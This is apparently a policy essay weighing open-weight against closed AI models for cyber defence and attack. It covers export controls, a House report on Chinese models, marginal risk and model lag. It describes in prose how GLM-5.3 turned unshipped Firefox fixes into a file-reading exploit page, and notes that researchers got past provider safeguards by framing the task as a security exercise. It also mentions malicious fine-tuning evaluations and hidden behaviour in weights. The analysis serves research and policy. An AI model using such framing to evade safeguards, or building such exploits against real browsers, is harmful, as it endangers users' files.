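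The podcaster Rob Wiblin, whom Lambert quotes, said in April that Mythos in the hands of criminals or hostile states "would be an actual disaster". That risk is a reason to restrict a few models rather than all of them. *Beyond the Binary* (2026) proposes allowing openness "where risks can be responsibly managed" and pairing it with spending on monitoring and public readiness.

Restrictions on open weights are hard to enforce across borders. Khawam (2026), in *How Export Controls Can—and Cannot—Reduce the Risks of Open-Weight Models*, argues that export controls can still work, but only at the right chokepoints, because developers lose control of the weights once they publish them. An American ban on releasing weights wouldn't bind Z.ai or Moonshot, which make the strongest open-weight models. China's proposed export rules could therefore restrict stronger open-weight models than any American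 law could.

Some people who fear advanced AI don't consider open weights the urgent problem. In *Open Weight Models are not the immediate problem*, danielms (2026) argues that governments should stop the leading companies from building AI that improves itself, and that they can do this without banning open-weight models. The author works for a company that serves such models.

### The case for closed models with verified access

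Restricted access can give defenders a better model than attackers have, which equal access cannot do. Anthropic applied this reasoning to Mythos Preview. Its partners in Project Glasswing, the programme for selected defenders, found more than 10,000 vulnerabilities in critical software. Fasano and colleagues describe this as a head start before attackers had similar models.

This is the strongest evidence for verified access, because it shows defenders doing a great deal of work with a hosted model. But the count comes from Anthropic and covers flaws found rather than fixed. The benefit also depends on who gets access, since a hospital outside the programme gained only if its software suppliers fixed their products and it installed the fixes.

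Security leaders made a similar complaint in June, when the US government's order took Anthropic's two newest models away from customers. iTnews' *Security leaders say lift export controls for Anthropic's Mythos-class models* summarises their view that limits on access put defenders at a disadvantage. They wanted a closed model back, so they were objecting to narrow access rather than arguing for open weights.

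Z.ai has tried a small version of the same idea. According to Axios' *A Chinese lab's new model is nearly as good at hacking* (2026), it first offered GLM-5.3 only to selected security partners in controlled environments and planned to publish the weights about two weeks later. That leaves time to find some flaws but hardly enough to install the fixes on most computers.

### The objection to Chinese weights

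On 20 November 2026 John Moolenaar and Andrew Garbarino, two Republican committee chairs in the US House of Representatives, published a report on American companies' use of Chinese open-weight models (House Homeland Security Committee and House Select Committee on China, 2026). They find that cost, customisation and near-frontier performance drive adoption, and that the United States has no competitive open-weight alternative at the same price. But they object to the developers, who they say increasingly answer to Beijing.

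The chairs' evidence of adoption comes from Airbnb, DoorDash and Anysphere, which makes the coding tool Cursor. Bot Mutiny's *Airbnb, DoorDash, Cursor Use Chinese AI, House Says* (2026) relays some of the figures. Airbnb runs customised versions of Alibaba's Qwen models for customer support, including an assistant that handles about 80,000 interactions a day. Another model summarises roughly 250,000 support cases. The chairs call the three companies "illustrative, not exhaustive". None of the uses Smalley lists in *US companies’ use of Chinese open weight AI draws rebuke* (2026) is security work. The report is therefore good evidence that large companies use these models, but it doesn't measure the shift among security teams.

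The chairs compare these models with network equipment from the Chinese companies Huawei and ZTE. American carriers kept buying that equipment after an official warning in 2012, and Congress later funded a $5 billion programme to replace it. The chairs fear that dependence on Chinese models will follow the same course: "What begins as cheap to adopt can become costly to depend on". Some new licences already require large commercial users to negotiate separate agreements.

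The comparison is only partly convincing. An AI model is harder to trace than a radio on a cell tower, because companies can adapt it, rename it and build it into other products. But it should be easier to replace once found. The chairs estimate that replacing such models can take months of work, but say removing embedded equipment takes years. Airbnb's copies also run on a US-based provider's infrastructure, so using them doesn't send customers' messages to Alibaba.

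The chairs recommend banning Chinese models from federal contract work and sensitive infrastructure, and supporting American open models. A ban would reduce the risk of hidden behaviour in the weights, which the chairs warn ordinary evaluations may not detect. It would not stop attackers from downloading the same models. It would also presumably apply to a security company that investigates break-ins for a federal agency. If the ban took effect before a comparable American open model was available, that company would have to use a weaker local model or return to hosted ones.

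### US policy since 2024

The US government last reviewed open weights in general in 2024. NTIA, the Commerce Department's agency for telecommunications and information policy, counted confidentiality among the benefits, because users don't have to share data with third parties. It also warned of risks to national security and of unclear accountability. It recommended that the government monitor the most capable open models but not restrict them yet.

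US policy has since moved from monitoring open models to promoting American ones. The Trump administration's AI Action Plan of July 2025 encouraged developers to release open models. In September 2026 Congress advanced a bill to promote American open-source models and publicise the risks of Chinese ones (The Star, *Congress advances new bill to give US edge in open-source AI race*, 2026). Two senior House Republicans have urged President Trump to back low-cost American models (The Jerusalem Post, *US Republicans urge Donald Trump to boost AI to counter China models*).

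The US government has so far treated open weights more as a matter of competition with China than as a danger in themselves. In June 2026 it forced a developer to withdraw models because of their hacking abilities, but those models were closed.

### What a new release adds for attackers

Supporters of open release often ask about marginal risk:

marginal risk = expected harm with the release − expected harm without it

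If attackers can already do something with existing tools, a new model that does it equally well adds little harm. OpenAI used this reasoning for gpt-oss, the open-weight model it released in 2025. After training the model to perform malicious tasks under controlled conditions, OpenAI concluded that it was not "substantially" more dangerous than existing models. Transformer's *Can open-weight models ever be safe?* objects that this standard keeps changing and that OpenAI applied it without outside oversight.

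A simple calculation supports the objection. Suppose each new open model makes attackers 10% more effective than the one before, and every developer considers 10% too small to matter. After ten releases, attackers are

1.1^10 ≈ 2.6

times as effective, although no single release ever looked dangerous. A developer could avoid this by comparing each model with what was available on a fixed date.

The result also depends on which existing tools a new model is compared with. Moonshot compares its open models with the strongest model, open or closed. But attackers can't use closed models freely, and Saxe doubts that they will rely on services that monitor and block them. If Saxe is right, the fairer comparison is with the best earlier open model. By that standard GLM-5.3 added a lot, since in Z.ai's own tests it completed more than three times as many exploitation tasks as GLM-5.2.

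The best experiment so far comes from the research group Epoch AI. In *AI can turn public security fixes into working exploits*, Ament, Edelman and Barry (2026) studied the patch gap, the time between the publication of a security fix and its arrival on users' computers. They gave GLM-5.3 the fixes for the Firefox browser that Mozilla had published but not yet shipped. The model worked out the underlying flaws and built a web page that could read a file from a visitor's computer without the visitor doing anything more than loading the page.

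The attack worked on all six Firefox versions released between 17 September and 26 October. Attacking each version took between 12 and 48 hours and cost about $1,000 in computing. For the most recent versions, the published fix wasn't enough by itself, so GLM-5.3 also had to find and use an unpublished flaw. The researchers described the task as a security exercise, and no provider's safeguards stopped them.

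The attack would cost a beginner more than these results suggest, because the team spent more than $100,000 on its Firefox work, including building a realistic test environment. Similar spending on Google's Chrome browser produced no successful attack. Lambert adds that an attacker with a working exploit still has to get victims to visit the page. To measure marginal risk, someone would have to repeat the test with GLM-5.2 and also with skilled people working without AI.

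Evidence from real attacks is harder to interpret. The House chairs cite public reports that an attacker breached several large South Korean banks and other financial institutions in late September and early October. The attacker used a Chinese open-source testing tool with a DeepSeek model, so the case is evidence of harm from open weights but not from GLM-5.3. So many critical flaws were also disclosed in October that some people called it "Black October", but disclosures rise whether defenders or attackers are finding more flaws. When Lambert first wrote that little had changed, GLM-5.3's weights had been public for just over a month, and victims often take longer than that to discover a break-in.

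### How long the lag is

The gap between closed and open models determines how long defenders have before attackers can run similarly capable models without supervision. AISI compared GLM-5.2 with earlier closed models on 70 short hacking tasks and on simulated company networks. CAISI made its own comparison. Barry's *Open-weight AI models are 6-7 months behind on cyber* assesses GLM-5.3 using Epoch AI's index of hacking ability.

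| Assessment | Open model | Closed model at a similar level | Lag |
|---|---|---|---|
| AISI, short tasks | GLM-5.2 | Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.3-Codex | 4 months |
| AISI, simulated networks | GLM-5.2 | Claude Opus 4.5 | Just under 7 months |
| CAISI, hacking ability | GLM-5.2 | Claude Opus 4.6 | 4 months |
| Barry, index | GLM-5.3 | The best closed models of the time | 6 to 7 months |

AISI had measured a lag of 6 to 10 months for open models released between January and September 2025, so the gap seems to have narrowed. AISI considers the network result weaker evidence because it has fewer networks than short tasks. In its main example, a 32-step attack that would take a human expert about 20 hours, nobody defends the network. AISI also warns that GLM-5.2's results can't be used to predict whether open models will match the large jump that Mythos Preview and GPT-5.5 made in April.

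GLM-5.3 may have matched part of that jump. It came out less than five months after Mythos Preview, and Fasano and colleagues found that it too could build complete exploits on its own. The House chairs cite an American developer's finding that the two models are comparable, and conclude that the assumption of a safe six-month lead no longer holds for cybersecurity. On Barry's index, GLM-5.3 appears to lag by at least six months. That lag is compatible with the exploit results, because a model may catch up on exploits while remaining behind on other hacking tasks.

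Whether a given lag is long enough depends on how quickly defenders use it. Suppose software makers need two months to find and fix the flaws that a new closed model reveals, and their customers need another two to install the fixes. A seven-month lag then leaves three months to spare, and a four-month lag leaves none. These figures are invented, and real repair times vary widely, but the example shows why a few months matter. The head start also begins only when defenders get access to the closed model, not when its developer finishes it.

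A short lag strengthens both sides' arguments because it makes open weights more useful to both responders and attackers who can't use a hosted model. The House chairs want to penalize Chinese developers who copy American models' abilities by collecting their outputs. If that worked, it would lengthen the lag for everyone, including American defenders who run those developers' models.

### Whether hosted services can meet the need

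If hosted services met every defender's needs, the security argument for open release would be much weaker. They already meet nearly all the needs of a large bank with verified access, but a penetration tester whose client forbids outside processing can't use them for that client's work.

Nobody has counted how many defenders fall into each group. Supporters of verified access cite the 10,000 vulnerabilities found, and supporters of open release cite Hugging Face's refusals, but neither measures unmet need. Providers could publish how many security teams apply for verified access, how many they reject and how long approved users wait. A low rejection rate and short waits would weaken the case for releasing the most capable weights, but defenders would still need some local model.

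### Who gains more from equal access

Saxe expects defenders to gain more. They outnumber attackers, have far more GPUs and can check their software before releasing it. Skilled attackers can already break into almost any organisation, so they have less to gain from AI. Saxe also notes that AI tools for tricking people have been available for years without transforming crime.

The last point is weak evidence about exploits, because deceiving an employee and finding a flaw in a browser require different skills. The other points are more persuasive for a company such as Mozilla than for a hospital. For example, after Ament and colleagues reported the unpublished flaw that GLM-5.3 had found in the Epoch AI experiment, Mozilla fixed it in the Firefox version released on 27 October. The same model helped both to attack Firefox and to repair it, and the outcome depended on who used it first.

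Defenders' fixes can also help attackers. Each published fix gives a model like GLM-5.3 a clue to the flaw, even when defenders found it through a programme such as Glasswing. Firefox and Chrome now release updates every week. If a fix becomes public just after one update and ships with the next, an attacker who needs 12 hours to build an exploit has about six and a half days to use it. Fixes for most other software take longer to reach users.

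Equal access therefore probably helps organisations that can find flaws and ship fixes within days, and harms those that wait months for someone else's update. Ament and colleagues decline to judge the overall balance. They recommend keeping fixes private until ready to ship and getting them to users faster, which would help defenders whether or not developers keep releasing weights.

### What follows from the Hugging Face case

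Delangue generalises from one successful investigation in his claim about fending off millions of attacks. Papadatos, whom The Next Web also cites, calls the claim overstated. The case shows that a capable local model can be more useful in an emergency than stronger models that refuse the work. But it doesn't show how much GLM-5.2 helps attackers, because the attackers used OpenAI's closed models.

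The work also consisted mostly of reading logs and decoding stolen data, and required little skill at writing exploits. The case therefore supports releasing models at GLM-5.2's level more than it supports releasing GLM-5.3, whose largest reported security gains were in exploitation. It is unknown how much GLM-5.3 would have improved the investigation.

The safety advocates' lesson has a similar weakness. OpenAI's agents ran without the usual classifiers and with a developer's computing power, and a model trained to be persistent took most of the actions. An open-weight model that matches them on a benchmark might not be able to carry out the same attack.

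Researchers could test this more directly by giving attackers and defenders on a practice network the same new open model, then repeating the exercise with only the models available before its release. If attackers reached the data in 30% of runs without the new model and 45% with it, the release would have helped them more than it helped the defenders. If they succeeded in only 20% with it, the defenders would have gained more.
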